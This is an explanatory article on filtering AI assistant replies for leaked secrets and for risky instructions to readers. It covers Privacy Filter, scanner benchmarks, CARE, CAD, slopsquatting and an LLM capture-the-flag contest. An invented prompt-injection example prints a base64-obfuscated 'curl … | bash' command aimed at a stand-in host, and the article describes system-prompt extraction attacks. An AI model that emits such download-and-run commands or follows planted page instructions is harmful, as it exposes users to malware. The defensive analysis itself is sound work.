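A token classifier labels each token of a text according to its context. It is meant to detect secrets the way a person reading "the door code is 4417" does, from the words around the number. OpenAI released a token classifier called Privacy Filter on 22 April 2026, which is free to download and adapt.

According to the model card by OpenAI (2026), Privacy Filter began as a small language model that predicted the next token. OpenAI replaced the part that chooses the next token with one that assigns labels, and changed the model to read in both directions. Each of its eight layers can process a token using the 128 tokens on either side of it. The model has 1.5 billion parameters but uses only about 50 million of them for any one token, so it can run on a laptop or in a web browser. It accepts up to 128,000 tokens at once.

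The labels cover eight categories: private names, addresses, email addresses, phone numbers, web addresses and dates, plus account numbers and secrets. The secret category includes passwords and API keys but is meant to exclude sample keys and placeholders.

To mask a whole password, the model also has to find where the password starts and stops. Each category therefore has four labels. Three mark the beginning, inside and end of a sensitive stretch of text, called a span, and the fourth marks a span of a single token. One more label for ordinary text brings the total to 33. If the model chose the most likely label for each token separately, it might label a three-token password beginning, ordinary and end, which would leave the middle token visible. Privacy Filter instead uses the Viterbi algorithm, which compares complete sequences of labels and picks the permitted one with the highest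 score. The faulty sequence isn't permitted, because an ordinary label can't come right after a beginning label.

Developers can adjust these scores with six settings. Making it easier for the filter to start and continue a span raises recall because the filter masks more text, while making it harder raises precision. These settings work without retraining, but a company that wants a new category or a different definition of a secret has to train the model further.

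A developer can instead define a secret in a written instruction to a general language model, by giving it the reply and asking whether it contains a credential that this user should not see. The model could recognise that a pet's name is a password because the user said so three messages earlier. But it is slower and more expensive, and if another company runs it, the secret leaves the developer's control. The model may also copy the secret inexactly, and then the filter can't find it in the reply to mask it.

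### What counts as a miss

A test can count how many characters or tokens of the secrets a filter masked, how many whole spans it found, or how many documents it left entirely clean. These scores can differ widely for the same output. Suppose a reply contains three 40-character keys, and the filter masks two completely and 36 characters of the third. Its recall is 97% by character (116 of 120) but 67% by exact span (two of three), and the document counts as a failure. An attacker could do little with the four visible characters, so the character score is the fairest here.

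Token-level recall can be the most misleading measure when secrets differ greatly in length. A private key might take up 1,000 tokens and a password only four. If a document contains one such key and nine such passwords, a filter that masks only the key recalls 1,000 of 1,036 secret tokens, or 96.5%, but misses nine of the ten secrets.

Benchmarks often combine precision and recall into an F1 score, which is 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall). F1 weights missed secrets and false alarms equally. This is often wrong for a filter on secrets, because one leaked password can do far more harm than several hashes masked by mistake.

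Even a filter with high recall per secret can be likely to miss at least one when there are many secrets. Suppose a filter catches 98% of secrets and a set of documents contains 50. If misses are independent, the chance that the filter catches all 50 is 0.98^50, or about 36%, so the chance that it misses at least one is about 64%. To bring that below 1%, the filter would need a recall of about 99.98% per secret.

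Misses are rarely independent. A filter without a pattern for one issuer's keys will miss all of them, so a few documents may leak every key while most leak none. The 64% figure is then too high for a typical set of documents and far too low for a company that uses that issuer.

### Scanners before 2026

*SecretBench* (2023) introduced a public dataset of real code for comparing scanners. The dataset contains 97,479 labelled strings, found by searching 818 GitHub repositories with 761 patterns. Of these strings, 15,084 were true secrets. Basak and colleagues then ran nine scanners on the same repositories, and the table gives the results for six. Recall here is the share of distinct secrets that a scanner found at least once in the repository.

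| Scanner | Alerts | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub Secret Scanner | 1,721 | 75% | 36% |
| Gitleaks | 45,932 | 46% | 88% |
| Commercial X (name withheld) | 86,607 | 25% | 48% |
| ggshield | 167,046 | 19% | 46% |
| TruffleHog | 90,982 | 6% | 52% |
| SpectralOps | 1,547,994 | under 1% | 67% |

No scanner did well on both measures. GitHub's scanner raised few false alarms but missed most of the secrets, and more than half of Gitleaks' alerts were false. Basak and colleagues traced missed secrets to faulty patterns, missing rules and file types that a scanner skipped. One scanner ignored web pages to avoid false alarms, although web pages were among the files that most often contained secrets. The scanners also found different secrets. Gitleaks reported only 18% of the true secrets that ggshield found, so running both would have caught more than either alone.

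The recall figures would be lower if they counted every copy of a secret. GitHub's scanner matched only 3% of all occurrences by file, line and version. A developer cleaning up code often needs to find only one copy, because cancelling the key makes every copy useless, but an output filter has to mask them all, because any copy it misses gives the reader the key.

The results are also out of date because the scanners have since had years of updates. SecretBench contains only secrets that matched one of its 761 patterns, so a scanner's recall on all secrets may be lower. It also differs from the text an assistant produces. Private keys, which start with a standard header, make up 38% of its true secrets, and passwords make up 1%. An assistant that reads email will probably encounter a much larger share of passwords. In GitGuardian's 2026 report, generic secrets, which no issuer-specific pattern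 covers, account for half of incidents.

Later studies have reused the benchmark in ways that make comparison difficult. *Secret Breach Detection in Source Code with Large Language Models* (2025) used a random sample of 30,000 of the more than 82,000 strings that are not secrets, which alone can raise a detector's precision. For example, a detector that catches 90% of the true secrets and wrongly flags 10% of the other strings would have a precision of 62% on the full benchmark and 82% with the smaller sample.

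### What Privacy Filter's scores measure

Privacy Filter has two reported F1 scores, 96% and 97.43%. Both are token-level scores on PII-Masking-300k, a synthetic collection of texts in six languages. The 96% score, which OpenAI's announcement reports with 94.04% precision and 98.04% recall, is based on the dataset's own labels after an automatic clean-up removed some obvious errors.

The second figure, 97.43%, comes from a corrected version of the labels. Privacy Filter had flagged many spans that the dataset did not label, and OpenAI had another of its models, GPT-5.4, decide which of these were personal data. OpenAI then left about 10,000 such spans out of the scoring. Human reviewers checked 100 of the decisions and agreed with all of them. The correction raised precision to 96.79% and left recall almost unchanged at 98.08%. Neither GPT-5.4 nor the reviewers checked for personal data that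 both the dataset and the filter had missed, so the true recall may be lower.

The span-level F1 scores are 92.6% and 94.2%. All of these figures combine the eight categories, so they are weak evidence of performance on secrets alone.

OpenAI tested how well Privacy Filter detects secrets on CredData, a collection of code with labelled credentials. The filter's recall was 96.5% by token and its precision was 74.7%, so about a quarter of the tokens it flagged were not part of a labelled secret. Its F1 score was 84.2% by token but 61.7% by span. OpenAI attributes part of the gap to spans that the filter found but marked too short or too long. The model card does not report how many secrets the filter missed entirely, the figure that would matter most to a company deciding whether to rely on it.

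The model card also reports less encouraging results from a smaller test, for which OpenAI generated short English texts. Privacy Filter caught 71% of the secrets when a clue such as "my password is" came before the value, 42% when the clue came after it and 36% when there was no clue. It raised almost no false alarms. Recall may be higher in code because a variable name such as "api_key" usually stands just before the secret. An assistant's reply can contain code or ordinary prose, and the CredData result is probably too optimistic for the prose.

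The model also has trouble when a clue is far from the secret it identifies. In another test, a text said that a certain word would stand for an account number and gave the number much later. Recall fell as the distance grew. OpenAI suspects that the training data contained too few such cases. The architecture also limits the distance, because eight layers that each reach 128 tokens can carry information across about 1,000 tokens at most.

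In the six languages of PII-Masking-300k, F1 ranged from 91% for Dutch to 93% for English. OpenAI also generated texts in 13 other languages, where F1 ranged from 76% for Hausa to 93% for Portuguese. Russian scored 90% and Arabic 88%. The model card doesn't give separate figures for secrets in any of these languages. A key looks much the same in every language, and mainly the words around it change.

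Unusual formatting caused more errors. Extra spaces inside the sensitive string reduced recall to 63%, and spelled-out digits reduced it to 67%. Line breaks reduced precision to 45% because the filter mistook fragments of web addresses for names. The filter still caught 98% of addresses written with "dot" or "at" instead of punctuation. OpenAI generated all these texts from a list of known tricks, so an attacker who can test disguises against the filter may evade it more often.

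The model card also lists errors that OpenAI expects, but does not give their frequency. Privacy Filter may miss keys in new formats and secrets split up by other code. It may also mask sample keys and hashes, so reading the context does not fully solve the problem of false alarms on hashes, which entropy checks also have.

### An independent test

In *OpenAI Privacy Filter*, Uppala (2026) tested the released model on 32 benchmarks in 14 languages. On 2,000 texts from the collection OpenAI used, the model's span F1 was 85.5%, compared with 92.6% in OpenAI's own test. The two tests prepared the labels differently, which may explain some of the gap. On five other English collections of personal data, its F1 was between 45% and 60%.

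On synthetic medical consultations, Privacy Filter caught 82% of the personal data, but only 32% of what it flagged was correct. Some of the false alarms arose because the dataset labels only details about the person asking the question, so flagging a relative's name counts as an error. OpenAI found that training the filter on a tenth of the dataset raised its token F1 from 54.5% to 96.2%. A company with its own definition of sensitive data can therefore expect poor results at first and large gains from training on a modest amount of labelled text.

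Without further training, Privacy Filter scored higher than Microsoft's Presidio, a widely used open-source tool, on all six English collections of personal data. GPT-4o, a general language model, did better than Privacy Filter on medical, legal and financial text, catching 95% of the personal data in the medical consultations. Privacy Filter did better on texts full of items in a regular format, such as phone numbers, possibly because GPT-4o often copied too much or too little text. GPT-4o is an old model, so a current one might do better.

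Uppala also concludes that about 500 labelled examples are enough for XLM-RoBERTa, an older and smaller model, to overtake Privacy Filter on synthetic English text. However, the scoring favoured XLM-RoBERTa, because Uppala accepted any overlap with the right span as a hit for that model but required exact boundaries from Privacy Filter.

The lowest scores were 4% for Persian and 3% for Ukrainian, far below OpenAI's results for Arabic and Russian. Uppala used a general benchmark for finding people's names, while OpenAI used texts written to contain private data. Privacy Filter is meant to ignore the names of public figures, and even its English score on the general benchmark was only 40%. The low scores are a reason to test the filter before using it in those languages, but they don't measure how well it finds other private data, such as phone numbers.

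The study is a single-author preprint and gives no separate score for secrets, so the only figures for credentials in code come from OpenAI.

### Secrets that arrive in pieces

All of these tests gave the detector a complete text, but an assistant usually sends its reply in chunks. Suppose a key consists of "key_" and 16 random characters. One chunk ends with "key_7Qm2" and the next begins with the remaining 12 characters. A filter that checks each chunk separately finds too few characters after the prefix in the first and no prefix in the second, so it passes both and the complete key appears on the user's screen.

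Because the key is 20 characters long, the filter can prevent this by always holding back the last 19 characters it has received. When the next chunk arrives, the filter adds it to the held text, searches the combined text, masks any key and releases everything except the new last 19 characters. This way, the filter receives the whole key before any part of it can reach the screen. When the reply ends, the filter checks and releases the rest.

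The delay depends on the longest string that the filter has to recognise. At 50 tokens a second and four characters a token, the model writes 200 characters a second, so 19 characters take about a tenth of a second. Anthropic's API keys have about 108 characters, according to Zhao and colleagues, so they cause a delay of about half a second. A private key of 1,700 characters would take more than eight seconds, but the filter can start masking at the standard header and stop at the closing line, without waiting for the whole key. After the initial delay, text appears at the usual speed, so readers may not notice a short delay.

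A filter can also hold text back only when the latest characters could be the start of a key, so most sentences appear without delay. This works for keys with a fixed prefix. An entropy check has to wait until the string is complete, and a classifier needs some of the words that follow it. Waiting for 128 more tokens, which is how far Privacy Filter can look ahead in a single layer, would take about two and a half seconds. A filter that waits for fewer may miss a password that only the later words would identify.

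### What a placeholder reveals

After finding a secret, the filter has to put something in its place. The choice determines how much the reader can still work out.

| Placeholder | Example | What it reveals |
|---|---|---|
| Blank | [REDACTED] | Where something is missing |
| Typed | [PASSWORD] | Also what kind of secret it was |
| Numbered | [PASSWORD_1] | Also which mentions refer to the same secret |
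| Hashed | [PASSWORD_9f3a] | Also whether the secret occurs in other texts, and whether a guess is right |

LiteLLM uses the blank form. Privacy Filter uses typed placeholders by default and offers the blank form as an option. The type helps someone repairing a server see which credential to replace, but it also shows an attacker that the file contains a password worth looking for.

Typed placeholders can confuse readers when several values have the same type. In the example email in OpenAI's announcement, the recipient, Jordan, and the signer, Maya Chen, both become [PRIVATE_PERSON]. Numbering the placeholders would distinguish the two people without revealing anything about their names.

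A hashed placeholder contains part of a fingerprint of the secret, so the same password gets the same placeholder in every document. This helps an administrator trace a leaked key through many log files. But anyone who knows the method can hash a guess and compare the result with the placeholder. A four-digit PIN has only 10,000 possible values, and a modern graphics card can try all ten-digit phone numbers within seconds. A long random key is safe because it has too many possible values to try. For short secrets, the filter should add a separate hidden key to the hash calculation so that outsiders can't test guesses.

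Some programs show part of the secret instead. A log in LiteLLM's documentation shows the first 12 characters of an API key, followed by asterisks. This hides enough of a long key, but the same rule would show most short passwords in full.

### When the filter's own records leak

Privacy Filter's detailed output includes the original value of each item it found, as does the report that AWS returns to developers. A developer who saves Privacy Filter's output for troubleshooting therefore also saves a copy of every secret it found.

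LiteLLM's *Incident Report* (18 March 2026) describes a leak of this kind. LiteLLM lets customers add their own checks, called guardrails, which can include output filters. While handling each request, the software keeps internal data it needs for the call, including the request headers, which often contain the sender's API key. This data was never supposed to enter the logs.

Some custom guardrails returned the entire request as their result instead of a short verdict. LiteLLM removed other material from these results before logging them, but not the headers. The keys in the headers therefore ended up in administrators' spending records and in traces, which developers use to follow a request through a system, and anyone with access to either could read the keys.

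The leak could occur only if a guardrail returned too much data, the result was logged, and someone had access to the logs. It did not let outsiders bypass LiteLLM's login or change what the models wrote. The company rated the leak high severity and lists its duration as unknown. The company does not report how many customers were affected or whether anyone misused a key.

LiteLLM fixed the fault in version 1.82.3 and advised customers to replace any credentials that might have reached the logs. The update stops new leaks, but keys already in stored logs still work until their owners cancel them. A filter on the assistant's replies would not have caught this leak, because the keys never appeared in a reply.

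## Detecting instructions to the reader: methods and benchmark results

Unlike many API keys, a risky instruction to the reader has no standard format, so a detector has to judge its effect and compare it with the user's request. It can do this in six steps:

1. Find the places where the reply tells the reader to do something.
2. Decode and parse any command.
3. Judge what the command would do.
4. Look up the domains and software packages that the instruction names.
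5. Compare the instruction with the user's request and its provenance.
6. Pass the reply, explain the command, warn the reader or block the reply.

Two invented exchanges show what each step contributes. In the first, a user gives an assistant a link to a web page and asks for a summary of its advice on noisy laptop fans. The page contains a hidden instruction to add a repair command. The assistant's reply covers dust and blocked vents, then ends with a supposed fan update: "Open Terminal, paste this line and press Enter."

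```
curl -s $(echo Zml4LmV4YW1wbGUvcnVu | base64 -d) | bash
```

In the second exchange, a user asks how to reinstall their backup program, Acme, which no longer starts. The assistant finds Acme's help page and replies, "Open Terminal, paste this line and press Enter."

```
curl -s acme.example/install | bash
```

No real website can use an address ending in ".example", so neither command would download anything.

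### Finding the instruction

The first step looks for imperatives such as "open", "paste" or "call", and for code boxes, links and phone numbers. It must check for links because attackers can leave out the command, as they did with the Custom GPT that recommended a "backup domain". The fan reply and the Acme reply contain the same sentence, so both go on to the next step.

A filter that warned about every command would interrupt a lot of ordinary advice. In March 2026 Howard Oakley, who writes articles and software for Mac users, examined ChatGPT's advice on finding out whether a Mac had ever detected malware. According to The Eclectic Light Company's *Why does AI tell you to use Terminal so much?*, all five recommended procedures used Terminal commands, although two could easily be done without them. Oakley's explanation is that chatbots are built on words, and it is fairly hard to describe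 in words how to use an app's windows and menus.

None of the five procedures did what ChatGPT claimed. Some of the commands searched for log entries up to a year old, but the logs on Oakley's Macs went back about a month at most. Another was supposed to show whether the Mac's malware definitions were current, but it printed thousands of lines without a date or version number. Although no attacker was involved, a reader could have wrongly concluded that the Mac was clean. A filter that treats any command as a sign of attack could raise five alarms in a conversation like this, though one exchange doesn't show how often chatbots recommend Terminal.

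### Decoding and parsing the command

*CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a checker for commands that AI agents are about to run. Its early stages would also suit a reply filter. CARE first rewrites the command in a standard form. It unwraps commands that merely start another shell (the program that interprets typed commands), rejoins words split up with quotation marks and variables, and decodes base64. It does this without running anything, and keeps the original with the decoded version so that later checks can use both.

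In the fan reply, the string of random-looking letters decodes to "fix.example/run". A parser then builds a tree that shows which programs the command runs, with which arguments, and where their output goes. The two commands differ mainly in that the address is hidden in the fan reply, so their trees are nearly the same after decoding. In both, curl downloads a script and the vertical bar passes it to bash, which runs it.

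The tree prevents some simple mistakes. The command `rm` deletes files, but `echo "rm"` only prints two letters. A search for "rm" would flag both, while the tree shows that the second command is `echo`. An attacker might write a command that the parser can't read. If parsing fails and the text contains other signs of high risk, CARE blocks the command.

The parser also needs intact text in the format it expects. *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* (2026) analyses commands in published agent skills, using a dataset that had lost its line breaks. Without line breaks, a web address can end up next to an unrelated "bash" from the following line, and together they look like a download-and-run command. A separate fault sent blocks of JSON and YAML settings to a tool that expected shell commands, which made including one class of operation seem to double the count of risky items. After the correction,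 including that class raised the count from 705 to 706. A chatbot's replies also mix commands, settings and prose, so a reply filter could make both mistakes.

CARE handles only bash and similar shells on Linux, so a filter for Windows users would also need a PowerShell parser. CARE checks each command separately, so it could miss an attack that downloads a file with one command, makes it executable with a second and runs it with a third, because each might look acceptable alone. A reply filter can examine all three together if they are in the same guide.

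### Judging the effect

The third step assigns the command to a type of action, such as downloading and running a program, changing permissions, deleting files or sending data elsewhere. CARE uses a hand-made dictionary of commands, and certain options raise the risk. CARE also checks which files the command touches. Reading the file that names the Linux version is low risk, but adding a line to a startup file is high risk because the line will run at later logins. CARE treats any access to a file of secrets as dangerous, even if the command only reads it.

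CARE then adds up four scores:

risk = 0.3 × action + 0.3 × location + 0.3 × known pattern + 0.1 × structure

The known patterns are 139 rules, most of them based on public catalogues of attack techniques. The structure score covers signs such as unusual nesting. By default, CARE allows a command if its risk is below 0.15 and blocks it at 0.35 or above. In between, CARE blocks the command if one piece of evidence is strong enough alone, and otherwise uses a language model to decide. One command in the study would have started a script when the shell closed, which an attacker could use to keep access to the machine. It scored 0.60 for its action and zero for everything else, so its risk was 0.3 × 0.60 = 0.18. The language model classified it as dangerous, and CARE blocked it.

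Both invented commands download a script and run it, so this step can't tell them apart. More generally, identifying an action correctly can reveal little about how dangerous it is. *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* gives the example of writing a key to a settings file, which is an operation on a secret but is also part of nearly every skill that needs an API key.

### Looking up domains and packages

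Suppose a lookup shows that someone registered fix.example last week, while acme.example has belonged to Acme for ten years. The recent registration is useful evidence against the fan command, although legitimate new projects have new domains too. An old domain is weaker evidence of safety when anyone can publish there, as on Google Sites.

Many commands name a package instead of a domain. A package is a bundle of software that an installer fetches from a public registry, such as PyPI for Python or npm for JavaScript. Language models sometimes recommend packages that don't exist. In an attack that security researchers call slopsquatting, an attacker can register such a name and put malware under it, so that the next person who follows the same advice installs it.

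Spracklen and colleagues measured how often 16 models, released up to mid-2024, invented names of software packages. *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (Churilov, 2026) summarises their results and repeats the test on newer models. In the original 576,000 code samples, on average 5.2% of the packages that commercial models named did not exist, compared with 21.7% for open-source models. The models invented 205,474 different names, 81% of which were each produced by only one model.

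In April 2026, Churilov gave the same prompts to Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini 2.5 Pro and DeepSeek V3.2. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of the packages they named did not exist, and between 2.2% and 3.4% of their answers contained at least one such name. DeepSeek, the only open-weight model of the five, did about as well as Gemini and GPT. The prompts had been public since January 2025, so the models may have seen them in training, which would make the rates look too low.

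Earlier versions of Churilov's study reported rates about a quarter higher. The largest error came from Python libraries whose name in code differs from their package name, such as PyYAML, which programs load as "yaml". A filter that looked up every name in a reply's code would raise the same false alarms, so it should give more weight to the names in install commands.

A registry lookup can reliably catch a name that nobody has registered, but it will pass one that an attacker has already registered. *Names Can Hurt* (2026) tested small models that run on the user's own computer and found that half of the packages they wrongly recommended already existed on PyPI, as low-quality squats or lookalikes. Churilov counted a name as invented only if it did not exist when the model wrote it, so his rates leave out the mistakes that an existence check would miss.

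Churilov also found that within about six months, people had registered 25 of the 2,282 invented names, or about 1%. At least one of the new packages contained malware. Others may have been harmless reservations, since researchers and defenders register such names too. The models also suggested at least 23 names that had previously hosted malware. For 13 of these, npm has replaced the malware with a placeholder, so a filter that only checks whether a package exists would pass them.

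A better check would also consider the package's age, download count and any record of malware, and could compare its name with those of popular packages. All five models in Churilov's study invented the same 104 names, and 54 of these were one character away from a registered package. In such cases the filter could suggest the registered package, after checking that it is the one the user needs.

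Checking package names against the public registry would still leave some gaps. A command can install software directly from a web address, which bypasses the registry. A company's private packages don't appear in the public registry, so a filter may wrongly report them as invented. The result can also go out of date. If a user saves a guide and runs its commands a month later, an attacker may have registered the missing package by then.

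### Comparing the instruction with the request

The two replies differ most clearly at the fifth step. The first user wanted a summary but received a command, as in CloudSEK's demonstration, while the second wanted to reinstall a program and received the command to do so.

Provenance supports the same conclusion. If the app keeps a copy of every page the model has read, the filter can search those pages for the commands, addresses and phone numbers in the reply. For the fan reply, this search leads to the hidden text. A search for the decoded address will probably succeed even if the model reworded the attacker's sentence, because the attack works only if the address is intact. For the Acme command, the search leads to visible text on the software maker's own page.

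CARE can't make either comparison, because it receives only the command and some information about the file system. Liu, Ma and Vorobeychik (2026), in *Robust Context-Aware Detection of Malicious Instructions in Text*, built a detector called CAD that takes the request into account. CAD screens documents before an AI agent reads them and removes suspicious sentences. It uses an embedding model, which turns a text into a list of numbers that reflects its meaning. If φ stands for this model, CAD describes each sentence by two lists:

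- φ(sentence)
- φ(request + document) − φ(request + document without the sentence)

The second list measures what the sentence adds to the request and the rest of the document. For a request about noisy fans, a sentence about dust should add something different from a sentence about Terminal. A small neural network uses both lists to estimate the probability that the sentence is malicious. CAD removes the sentence if the probability is above 50%.

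Liu, Ma and Vorobeychik tested whether the context helped by removing parts of it and running the detector again. On AgentDyn, a benchmark of long agent tasks, the full version let 3.5% of standard attacks succeed, and the agent completed 36.7% of its tasks when there was no attack. Without the request, 7.9% of attacks succeeded and the agent completed 28.3% of its tasks. Without the surrounding sentences, 2.8% of attacks succeeded, but the agent completed only 16.7% of its tasks because CAD removed too much harmless text. The three versions performed about the same on the shorter tasks of AgentDojo, another benchmark. Context may matter most in long and varied conversations.

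### Choosing a response

In the fan reply, four findings support each other: the hidden address, the new domain, the unrelated request and the hidden text. The filter can block the instruction and leave the advice about dust. The Acme reply can pass, perhaps with an explanation that the command downloads Acme's installer and runs it with the user's permissions. The filter should base this explanation on the parsed command rather than the model's description, which an attacker may have influenced.

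A warning suits the cases in between. Suppose the first user had asked how to repair the fan, and the model had suggested the encoded command without reading any web page. The instruction would then fit the request, and there would be no hidden text as evidence against it. The encoded address and the new domain would still be reasons for concern, but a legitimate, badly written guide could contain both.

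An unexpected instruction isn't necessarily harmful either. *On Task, Off Track* (2026), a benchmark of prompt injection, uses a language model to judge whether the outcome an attacker wants would do harm. Under the judge's instructions, a harmful outcome must differ from the normal one and have a concrete and significant consequence, such as losing money, losing data or giving someone unauthorised access. A reply filter could use the same rule to avoid blocking a summary just because it ends with an unrequested tip. But the filter's task is harder, because it doesn't have the harmless answer and the attacker's goal, which the benchmark's judge receives.

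### What existing tests measure

A search of research preprints found no benchmark that directly tests whether a filter can spot risky instructions to a human reader. Such a benchmark would need complete conversations, with harmful and harmless replies that contain similar commands.

*Beyond Static Sandboxing* (2026) comes closest to testing the detection of instructions to the reader. When asked for a reverse shell, a connection that lets someone control a computer remotely, a small model wrote out the instructions as text. Security checks on the agent's actions missed this because the agent hadn't run anything. The researchers therefore used Llama Guard 3, Meta's general safety model, to classify the replies. It flagged all four dangerous texts and none of the three safe ones, usually in about a second.

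Seven texts are far too few to estimate an error rate. At the 95% confidence level, the results are compatible with a recall as low as 40% and a false positive rate as high as 71%. Also, the user in the reverse-shell example asked for something dangerous and was not deceived.

CARE has a much larger test, with 220 dangerous and 329 safe commands. Most of the dangerous ones come from public collections for testing security software, and most of the safe ones from a collection of everyday Linux commands. The table gives results for some of the guards that Liu, Zhang and colleagues compared.

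| Guard | Recall | False positive rate | Average time per command |
|---|---|---|---|
| 22 text patterns | 17% | 0% | 0.01 ms |
| Llama Guard 3 | 40% | 1.2% | 50 ms |
| Language model as judge | 67% | 11.3% | 46 ms |
| Granite Guardian (IBM) | 82% | 45.9% | 17 ms |
| CARE, rules only | 76% | 1.8% | 0.34 ms |
| CARE with language model | 76% | 0.9% | 2.32 ms |

Llama Guard 3 missed 60% of the dangerous commands in this test, but caught everything in the earlier test with seven texts. It is a general safety model and was given only bare commands, so neither result shows how well it would do on whole replies. Adding a language model to CARE's rules halved the false positive rate, but the difference was three commands and could easily be due to chance.

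CARE also had an advantage over the other guards, because the researchers chose its settings using commands from the same collections. It did worse on new ones, and its false positive rate rose to 8–13%, partly because the researchers had included harmless commands that look dangerous, such as one that deletes temporary files. Its reported scores imply a recall of about 59% on commands that misuse ordinary Linux programs, 54% on published exploits and 89% on disguised versions of known attacks.

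In another test, a language model wrote 600 commands in response to harmful requests, and the researchers ran them in an isolated environment. Without a guard, 75% of the commands succeeded. CARE's rules alone reduced this to 37%, but 53% succeeded when CARE also used the language model, because the model approved some commands that the rules had flagged. The same model had written the commands, which may have made it more lenient. A filter that uses one model to review another's replies could have the same problem if the two models are closely related.

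All these figures are for commands that an agent is about to run. CARE's labels don't depend on who wants a command or why, so some actions they mark as dangerous are ones a user might reasonably request. One example labeled dangerous deletes a computer's log files, which is also a crude answer to a user who asks how to free disk space.

CAD's tests include the request but measure a different outcome, how often attacks succeed. CAD reduced the success rate of standard attacks from 59.6% to zero on AgentDojo and from 50.0% to 3.5% on AgentDyn. It also reduced the share of tasks the agent completed when there was no attack, from 65.8% to 57.6% on AgentDojo and from 46.7% to 36.7% on AgentDyn. These lost tasks are the nearest equivalent to false alarms. Attacks adapted to the defence succeeded in about 8% to 9% of cases. The main results come from GPT-4o-mini, an old and fairly small model.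 CAD also works on text that enters an agent, and nobody in the study read a reply and decided whether to follow it.

Liu, Ma and Vorobeychik also tested PromptGuard 2, a detector from Meta's LlamaFirewall toolkit that looks for attempts to override a model's instructions. It made little difference, and standard attacks still succeeded in 56.1% of cases on AgentDojo. A reply that politely recommends a command may contain no such attempt, so the detector could have even less to find. The toolkit's CodeShield scanner looks for insecure code, but a one-line download command can be well written and still deliver malware.

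Other benchmarks test the model that writes the reply. BIPIA, an early example from 2023, measured whether models obeyed instructions planted in outside content. *TopicAttack* (2025) uses two sets of 900 questions whose source texts contain planted instructions for phishing, advertising or propaganda. An attack succeeds if the reply follows the planted instruction, for instance by including a phishing address. Researchers could use replies from successful attacks to test a filter's recall. To measure false alarms, they would also need harmless replies that recommend links.

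### False alarms from familiar words

Li, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *Defenses Against Prompt Attacks Learn Surface Heuristics*, examined why filters reject harmless text. They added words that are common in attacks, such as "sudo", to 113 harmless prompts and tested the prompts on five filters that screen for attacks. "Sudo" runs a command with administrator rights and often appears in legitimate repair advice. They then removed the added words and tested the prompts again.

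| Filter | Rejected with the words | Rejected without them |
|---|---|---|
| ProtectAI v2 | 53.9% | 23.8% |
| Lakera Guard | 58.5% | 47.7% |
| PromptGuard 2 | 11.5% | 1.7% |
| FMOPS | 86.7% | 78.7% |
| Deepset | 87.6% | 86.7% |

The words caused more than half of ProtectAI's false alarms and most of PromptGuard 2's. The last two filters rejected most of the prompts with or without the words. Li and colleagues also report increases of up to 49 percentage points, but those figures come from comparing the prompts containing the words with an unrelated set of safe prompts. The table is a fairer test because only the words change.

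The filters in this test check prompts, but a detector for replies could learn the same bias in training. If most of its harmful examples contain "sudo", "curl" or "bash" and few of its harmless ones do, it can score well by reacting to those words. Both the training data and the test should therefore include harmless troubleshooting replies that contain these words.

A detector can also learn to treat text as suspicious because of where it appears. Li and colleagues put two harmless exam questions in one prompt and gave them to a version of Llama 3 trained to resist injected instructions. It declined to answer 6% of the first questions and 90% of the second. The researchers attribute this to training data in which the attack usually comes last. In CAD, the malicious sentences appear at random points to avoid such a shortcut. The shortcut would also matter when checking AI replies, because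 a useful command often comes at the end of an explanation.

### When attacks are rare

Suppose an AI service produces 1,000,000 replies with commands, and 10 of them are hostile. The figure of 10 is invented, since nobody has published a reliable one. A filter with 95% recall would catch 9.5 of the 10 on average. With a false positive rate of 1%, it would also flag about 10,000 of the 999,990 harmless replies. Only about one in 1,050 flagged replies would be hostile.

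In general, with recall r, false positive rate f and a hostile share of p:

precision = r × p / (r × p + f × (1 − p))

False alarms would have to fall to 9.5 for half of the alarms to be true. The false positive rate would then be 9.5 / 999,990, or about 1 in 105,000. Better recall hardly helps, because a filter that caught all 10 hostile replies would still raise about 10,000 false alarms at the original false positive rate.

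Liu, Zhang and colleagues make a similar calculation for CARE, but assume that 1% of commands are dangerous. Out of 10,000 commands, CARE would catch about 76 dangerous ones, miss 24 and wrongly block about 90 safe ones, so nearly half of its alarms would be correct. If the share were 1,000 times lower, at 10 hostile replies in a million, the same error rates would give about 8 correct alarms and 9,100 false ones.

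A second check could remove many of the false alarms. If it kept 90% of the true alarms and only 1% of the false ones, about 8.6 true alarms and 100 false ones would remain, a precision of 8%. This assumes the two checks make unrelated mistakes. However, both may flag an unusual but legitimate command, so the improvement would probably be smaller.

A company can also use the filter where attacks are more common, such as on the ad-promoted shared chats with terminal commands that Trend Micro singled out. If one in ten of those chats were malicious, the original filter, with 95% recall and a 1% false positive rate, would have a precision of 91%.

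A filter that blocked 10,000 correct repair guides to stop nine or ten attacks would annoy many users, and some would look for the command on a site with fewer safeguards. A short explanation of what the command does would inconvenience them much less, and could appear with every command.

A small benchmark can't show that a filter is accurate enough to block replies at this scale. The 22 text patterns in the CARE comparison raised no false alarms on 329 safe commands, but at 95% confidence this only shows their false positive rate is below about 0.9%. To show a rate below 1 in 105,000, researchers would need to test about 315,000 harmless replies with no false alarms.

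## Contests, adaptive attacks and proofs about what filters can miss

Researchers can measure a filter's false positive rate with enough harmless replies, because ordinary users don't rewrite their requests to get past the filter. Recall is less stable because an attacker can change blocked text and try again, and usually needs to succeed only once.

A small miss rate adds up over many attempts, as it does over many secrets. If attempts were independent, an attacker would have a 63% chance of getting past a filter with 99% recall within 100 attempts, and a 99% chance within 500. In practice, an attacker who repeats an attack that the filter reliably recognises will never succeed, while one who learns from each refusal may need far fewer attempts.

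A fixed test set leaves out this learning, because its attacks don't change in response to the filter. This matters especially for published pages, such as the shared chats in the ad campaigns, because an attacker can test versions in private and publish only one that gets past the filter. Every visitor then sees that version.

### The SaTML 2024 competition

In a capture-the-flag contest, players compete to obtain a hidden string. Debenedetti, Rando and colleagues organised one at SaTML, a conference on secure machine learning, and described it in *Dataset and Lessons Learned from the 2024 SaTML LLM Capture-the-Flag Competition* (2024). The secret was six random letters and digits in the system prompt, the instructions a developer gives a model before the conversation starts. The models, GPT-3.5 and Llama 2, are long out of date, so the success rates don't carry over to current products,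 but the contest is still useful because teams built their own filters and then attacked each other's.

A defence could have three parts, each limited to 512 characters: extra instructions in the system prompt, a short Python program that edited the reply, and a second language-model call that could also edit it. The Python program received the secret, so it could search the reply for that exact string. The organisers checked that the model could still answer ordinary questions under each defence, and they accepted 44 of the 72 submissions.

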